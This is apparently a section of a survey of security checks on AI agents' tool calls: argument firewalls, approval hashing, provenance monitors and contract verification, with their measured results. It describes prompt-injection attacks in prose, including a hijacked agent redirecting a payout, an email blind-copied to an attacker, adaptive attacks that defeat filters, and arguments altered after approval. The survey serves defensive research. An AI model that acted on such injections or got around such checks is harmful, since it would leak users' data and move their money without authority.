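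To keep attackers from influencing the policy, Mellafe Zuvic requires that no part of it come from a language model's output, even when a developer writes it in advance. Progent and IntentFlow would not meet this requirement, because a model writes their policies. The rule seems stricter than necessary to stop attackers, since a web page can't influence a policy that a model wrote before reading the page, but it also protects against the model's own mistakes.

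### Where the check can run

A check near the tool has access to more information about what a call will do than a check near the model, but less about why the model made the call.

| Position | Conversation | Labels | Argument | Real effect |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Model provider | Yes | Only if the developer sends them | As the model writes it | Only for tools the provider runs |
| Agent framework | Yes | Yes, if the runtime keeps them | Before later conversions | No |
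| Proxy for the Model Context Protocol | Only if the agent's software sends it | For results that pass through the proxy | As the tool server receives it | No |
| Tool | Usually not | Only if the caller sends them | After the tool's own conversions | Yes |

The provider can restrict an argument while the model writes it, for example with a strict schema, but can't control what the developer's software does with the call afterwards. The framework is the natural place to check where an argument came from, because it holds both the conversation and any labels. Microsoft's Fides middleware runs in the framework, and PACT's contracts need the same information.

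A proxy for the Model Context Protocol (MCP) passes messages between the agent and its tool servers. It works with many frameworks and doesn't require changes to the tools, but it misses any tool that the agent calls without MCP.

A check at any of these three positions can't reveal what the tool's code does. Adam, Lu and colleagues (2026), in *Towards Practically-Secure Tools for AI Agents*, give the example of a tool that writes a file and also reports the file's size to an outside service. The tool's description doesn't mention the report, and nothing in the arguments shows it, yet for a proprietary project even the file's size could be a leak.

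One solution combines static analysis with sandboxing. The analysis lists everything the tool's code can do to files and the network. The tool's developer then wraps each of these operations in a small sandbox that enforces a policy for the current call, such as "write only in the workspace". The analysis also confirms that every operation has a sandbox.

Adam and colleagues tested this on three recorded coding sessions, each with a harmless and a harmful version. Their method made the right decision in all six cases, compared with five for static analysis alone and three for a fixed sandbox around the whole server. The test was small and assumed that a correct policy already existed for each call. The method also needs cooperation from the tool's developer and proof that the server is running the code the analysis examined.

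Some systems instead monitor the operating system. *AgentBouncer* (2026) intercepts system calls, the requests that programs make to open files or network connections. It can block one hidden action while the rest of the tool's work continues. But an email's recipient may not be visible at this level if the connection is encrypted.

No single position therefore works for every check. An origin check fits best in the framework, while the safest place to check a file path is where the tool opens the file.

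### What a list of tools lets through

Many frameworks have only a *capability gate*, which controls which tools the model can use. LangChain, LlamaIndex and the Stripe Agent Toolkit, the three toolkits in Mellafe Zuvic's June 2026 study, all work this way by default. Stripe's toolkit also limits what its access key may do, but within those limits it forwards whatever amounts, customers and redirect addresses the model supplies.

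To demonstrate the problem, Mellafe Zuvic gave LangChain a fixed tool call that changed a merchant's payout account to the attacker's. The call stood in for the output of a hijacked model. LangChain ran it against a simulated payment system because the tool was available and the account was a string. A companion test on LlamaIndex had the same result. The finding about Stripe comes only from reading the source code.

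The demonstrations don't give a success rate, but one is hardly needed for a capability gate, because it has no rule about argument values and passes any well-formed call to an available tool. Models vary in how often they write such a call. In a separate benchmark of 27 models, the average attempt rate was 60% for 12 cheaper models and 19% for 15 flagship models. Individual rates ranged from 0% for a preview of Gemini 3.1 Pro to 100% for GPT-4o mini. The benchmark also counted trials in which a model revealed a planted test string, so these rates don't measure tool calls alone.

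The wording of the attack mattered too. Mistral Large complied with 3% of crude instructions but 46% of instructions that presented the same action as part of the user's task.

Mellafe Zuvic's own check, ScopeGate, allows a call only if it passes four tests:

1. The operator's policy covers the tool.
2. Every restricted argument has a value on the operator's list.
3. Any payment is a finite number between zero and a set ceiling.
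4. If the action must not happen twice, the request has a key that identifies repeats.

ScopeGate blocked the payout call that LangChain had run. It also blocked 48 altered calls from a fixed test set, and all 29 unauthorised calls from a model that received the reason for each block and tried again. In another test it allowed all ten legitimate calls, but ten is too few to estimate how often it would obstruct real work. Because it relies on a list of accepted values, it would block the Slack invitation to Dora unless the operator had listed her address.

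### Firewalls that scan or rewrite arguments

ScopeGate is an *argument firewall*, a component that inspects argument values and allows, rewrites, refers or blocks the call. Others look for signs of a known attack. Yuan, Su and Zhao (2026), in *AEGIS*, describe one released in March that modifies the software libraries through which agents call models. When a model writes a tool call, Aegis pauses the agent and does the following:

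1. It extracts every string from the arguments, down to 32 levels of nesting. If there is too much to extract, it marks the call as suspicious.
2. It compares the strings with 22 patterns for seven kinds of risk, such as SQL injection, access to sensitive files and leaks of personal data.
3. It applies the developer's policies, which are JSON Schemas.

Aegis then allows the call, blocks it or holds it for a person to review. In the researchers' test, it blocked all 48 attacks and wrongly flagged 6 of 500 harmless calls. Those 6 were all database queries that contained a legitimate OR. The median delay was 8.3 milliseconds, and the delay was no more than 23.1 milliseconds for 99% of calls.

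The attacks all belonged to categories that Aegis has patterns for, so the perfect score shows little about attacks outside those categories. Patterns are also a poor defence against the email to the stranger. One pattern matches email addresses, but it would match the manager's address as well as the stranger's. A developer could write a policy that accepts only company addresses, but the pattern scan would add nothing to the protection from that allowlist.

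Aegis also misses any call that doesn't go through the modified libraries. If a tool runs model-written code in the same process, that code might be able to undo the modification.

*Indirect Prompt Injections* (Bhagwatkar, Kasa and colleagues, 2025) checks arguments with a language model instead of patterns. Its *Minimizer* receives the user's task, the tool's description and the proposed arguments, and removes any data that the task doesn't need. A second component, the *Sanitizer*, rewrites each tool result to remove planted instructions before the agent reads it. The table gives the results on AgentDojo with GPT-4o. The figures for CaMeL come from the CaMeL paper.

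| Defence | Tasks completed without an attack | Tasks completed under attack | Attack success rate |
|---|---|---|---|
| None | 83% | 50% | 58% |
| Minimizer | 70% | 50% | 18% |
| Sanitizer | 74% | 69% | 0% |
| Both | 58% | 59% | 0% |
| CaMeL | 54% | 55% | 0% |

The Minimizer mostly stopped attacks that tried to send private data out in an argument. It also deleted data that the tasks needed, and adding it to the Sanitizer lowered utility by 16 percentage points with no measured gain in security. These results support cleaning what the agent reads much more than rewriting its tool-call arguments. Deletion is also poorly suited to sink arguments, because an email without a recipient fails.

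One advantage of the Minimizer is that it never reads the web page, so a planted instruction can reach it only if the agent copies the instruction into an argument.

Both components call a model for every tool call, so they are much slower than pattern matching. On AgentDojo's attacked banking and Slack tasks, the firewall defence took 56 minutes in total, compared with 140 for CaMeL.

### Flaws in the benchmarks

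Bhagwatkar and colleagues treat their own perfect scores as a reason to distrust the benchmarks. Some of AgentDojo's injections overwrite information that the task requires, such as the amounts on a bill, so even an agent that ignores the attack can't complete the task. One of its Slack tasks counts as complete only if the recipient has exactly one new message, so an agent that sends the right message and an extra one fails. After they repaired such cases, an undefended GPT-4o agent completed 72% of attacked tasks, up from 61%. Published figures for utility under attack are therefore probably too low, and the error may differ between defences.

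ASB, which Shi and colleagues used to test Progent, has worse problems. It adds the attacker's tools to the agent's selection even if the agent did not choose them, then counts any use of them as a successful attack. When the agent could choose its tools freely, the attack success rate fell from 74% to 9% without any defence. Most of Progent's 70% baseline attack success rate may therefore be due to the benchmark's design. InjecAgent does not measure utility, so a defence that blocked everything would get a perfect score.

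All three benchmarks also use weak attacks. Bhagwatkar and colleagues built a stronger test from AgentDojo's Slack tasks in three stages. The first used existing attacks, the second disguised the instruction as ordinary metadata, and in the third a model used information about the defence to refine the text over ten rounds. The attack success rate against the Sanitizer rose from 0% to 12.5% and then to 30%. The final attacks succeeded 75.5% of the time against PromptArmor, which uses a language model to detect and filter out planted instructions. The "perfect security" in the paper's abstract applies only to attacks that the benchmarks already contained.

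### When the approved call changes

A tool call passes through several programs on its way to the tool, and any of them may alter it. In *Do Tool Calls Execute as Intended?*, Yang, Li and colleagues (2026) examined 47,828 shell commands that the coding agents Claude Code and Codex ran on Windows during ordinary work. Claude Code's Bash tool altered 12.0% of the commands that contained code, escape sequences or long text. When the change affected backslashes, the wrong action ran without any reported error 80.7% of the time. In other cases, a program removed quotation marks or cut off a long argument.

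These changes were accidental, but they undermine security because a check may approve one command while the computer runs another. Yang and colleagues' repair tool, INTACT, sends the command by a route that the faulty program doesn't parse, such as a file. If no such route exists, INTACT refuses the call. On their benchmark, it recovered 79.2% of the failures in which a call had changed.

A call can also change while it waits for a person's approval. Kodathala, Pollishetty and Cargill (2026), in *Approve What, Exactly?*, audited ten toolkits and could test this in eight. In four, someone could change the arguments after approval:

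- LangGraph and Agno run whatever arguments are in the saved conversation when it resumes.
- Pydantic AI takes the arguments from a message history that the caller supplies.
- CrewAI lets a later piece of code change arguments that an earlier one approved.

An attacker can't do this with text on a web page alone. They also need access to the saved run, the interface that resumes it, or the code that runs before the tool.

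Kodathala and colleagues' own system, ASU, prevents such changes by hashing the call. A *hash* is a short code computed from data, and in practice any change to the data changes the hash. ASU first converts the call to a canonical form. It makes file paths absolute, puts email addresses in lower case, splits commands into separate arguments and rejects arguments the tool did not declare. It then computes:

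```
h = SHA-256(canonical form of the call)
```

A gateway outside the agent's reach stores the call, and the user's phone signs an approval that includes `h` and a single-use number. The gateway then runs its stored copy. If the agent resubmits the call with different arguments, their hash doesn't match `h` and nothing runs. In more than 27,000 scripted trials, ASU stopped every substitution and every attempt to reuse an approval.

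The gateway must resolve symbolic links before it hashes a path. Otherwise, someone could redirect a link after approval and the hash would still match. Every program that checks the hash must also produce the same canonical form. Microsoft's Agent Governance Toolkit writes decimal numbers the way Python does, so three of five sample numbers would hash differently in another programming language. Such a mismatch blocks legitimate calls but doesn't let altered ones through.

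AttestMCP, a system in *Evaluating and Improving the Robustness of Large Language Models* (2026), signs a hash of each call's arguments and adds at most 0.1 milliseconds. A matching hash proves only that the call hasn't changed since it was signed, so a call that the model wrote because of an injection also gets a valid signature.

The approver also has to see the real arguments. Kodathala and colleagues asked 15 language models to approve or refuse an email that blind-copied an attacker. All 15 approved it when they read the agent's description, which left out the blind copy, but refused it when the gateway listed both recipients.

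An approval can also go out of date. *Temporary Authority, Permanent Effects* (2026) points out that LangChain and the OpenHands toolkit run an approved call without checking whether the approval still stands. *Agenra* limits how long an approval stays useful by giving each one a permit for a single exact call. The permit is used up even if the tool fails.

### What a refusal reveals

Blocking a call doesn't always end an attack, because the agent learns that the check refused it. In Chinaei's example, an agent tries to read someone's salary record. The refusal may reveal that the record exists, and an attacker can plant an instruction to email that fact to an outsider. Content matching can't connect the email to the record, since the agent never read the record. Garby and colleagues found a similar leak in CaMeL, where repeated failures could reveal a secret one bit at a time.

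Chinaei's defence, the Agentic Reference Monitor (ARM), came out in April 2026. It runs as an MCP proxy and keeps a provenance graph with nodes for tool calls, the data they return, individual fields of that data, and denied actions. Edges connect each call to its inputs and outputs. When ARM denies a call, it adds a *counterfactual edge* from the denied action to the agent's next call, because the denial might have influenced that call.

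ARM computes the trust of a call `c` from all the data that led to it:

```
MinTrust(c) = lowest trust of any data from which a path leads to c
```

It refuses the call if this value is too low, or if any path to the call includes a counterfactual edge. Fixed rules also block calls that, for example, contain passwords or request sensitive files.

Chinaei tested ARM on three scenarios and compared it with a simple check that accepts any value found in the agent's history:

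- The agent tries to read a protected file, then emails someone that the file exists.
- A formatting tool rewrites text from an untrusted email, and the agent sends the result.
- A contact record has a trusted name but an untrusted email address, and the agent writes to that address.

ARM blocked the final call in all three scenarios, and the simple check blocked none. Each decision took less than a millisecond. Chinaei designed each scenario around a feature that the simple check lacks, and the tests involved no language model, so they show that the graph works as intended but do not measure error rates.

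The file scenario is also less convincing because ARM refuses certain file paths by name before the tool runs. The agent gets the same refusal whether or not the file exists, so it learns ARM's rule but nothing about the file. A simpler defence would be to make all refusals work this way, giving no reason that depends on protected data.

The counterfactual edge is also crude. Chinaei acknowledges that ARM can block a harmless call just because it follows a refusal, and can miss a leak that takes several more steps. The published algorithm may have a larger problem. It records the second refusal as another denied action and links it to the next call. Read literally, this would make ARM refuse every later call in the session. None of the three scenarios continues long enough to test this.

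### When the supplier writes a false contract

A check that relies on tool contracts is only as reliable as the people who write them. *The Gate Is Only as Honest as Its Contracts* examines what happens when a supplier falsifies a contract that a gate relies on. The contract states what the tool needs before it can run, what it achieves, how risky it is and what authorisation it requires. The gate finds the lowest-cost sequence of tools that reaches the user's goal, and hides a risky tool from the model unless that tool is the next step and has authorisation.

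Falsely labelling a dangerous tool as low-risk exposed it in at most a quarter of cases, because the tool usually didn't fit into the sequence. Falsifying the descriptions of both what the tool needs and what it achieves exposed it every time, because it then appeared to complete the whole task in one step.

The paper's defence, ContractGuard, adds three checks:

1. The contract must have a trusted signature, or ContractGuard uses a trusted reference copy instead.
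2. Every field that the gate uses must match the reference copy.
3. After the tool runs, ContractGuard discards any effect that the contract did not declare before updating the gate's record of the task.

The researchers tried all 256 combinations of falsified fields and related tricks against eight dangerous tools. None defeated the three checks together, but every partial version failed against at least one combination. Through this search, the researchers also found a way around an early version of the second check, which compared only some of the fields. In tests with six commercial and open models, including Claude Opus 4.8, every model called the dangerous tool when a false one-step contract exposed it, and none did with ContractGuard in place.

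All of this depends on a genuine reference copy. If the supplier can change that copy too, ContractGuard will restore false values. The third check also comes too late to recall an email the tool has already sent. ARM offers more limited protection by recording a hash of each tool's schema at first use and refusing the tool if the schema later changes. This catches a supplier who changes the schema after gaining users' trust, but not one whose schema was false from the start.

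### Failing closed and its cost

A check *fails closed* if it refuses a call whenever it encounters an error or lacks the information to decide. It *fails open* if the call runs anyway. The difference can come down to one comparison. An early version of ScopeGate refused any payment above the ceiling, but computers have a special value called NaN, "not a number", which is never greater than anything:

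```python
if amount > ceiling: refuse()                                    # NaN passes
if not (isfinite(amount) and 0 <= amount <= ceiling): refuse()   # NaN fails
```

The second line is closer to the repaired version, which accepts an amount only after confirming that it is in range.

Failing closed also blocks legitimate work. In Adam and colleagues' tests, static analysis alone blocked an intended file write because it could not determine where the file would go. INTACT rejects every multi-line command for the Windows command prompt because it has no way to deliver one unchanged. If many agents share one central gateway, a gateway outage stops all of them.

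*Kairos* (2026) argues that a check which must immediately allow or refuse an action will inevitably make mistakes, because it often can't determine where a value came from or what the user wanted. It proposes holding an action's effects in a staging area while the agent continues, and releasing or discarding them later. The check must then report any discarded effect to the agent, or the agent will continue as if the action had succeeded. Holding is more practical for a file change than for a message whose reply the agent needs.

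Refusals also disrupt the agent's work less if it has a permitted alternative. In *Temporary Authority, Permanent Effects*, agents had permission to publish a software release until the researchers withdrew it without telling them. The instructions named a test site as a fallback, which had its own permission. After 11 of 12 such withdrawals, the agents published to the test site instead.
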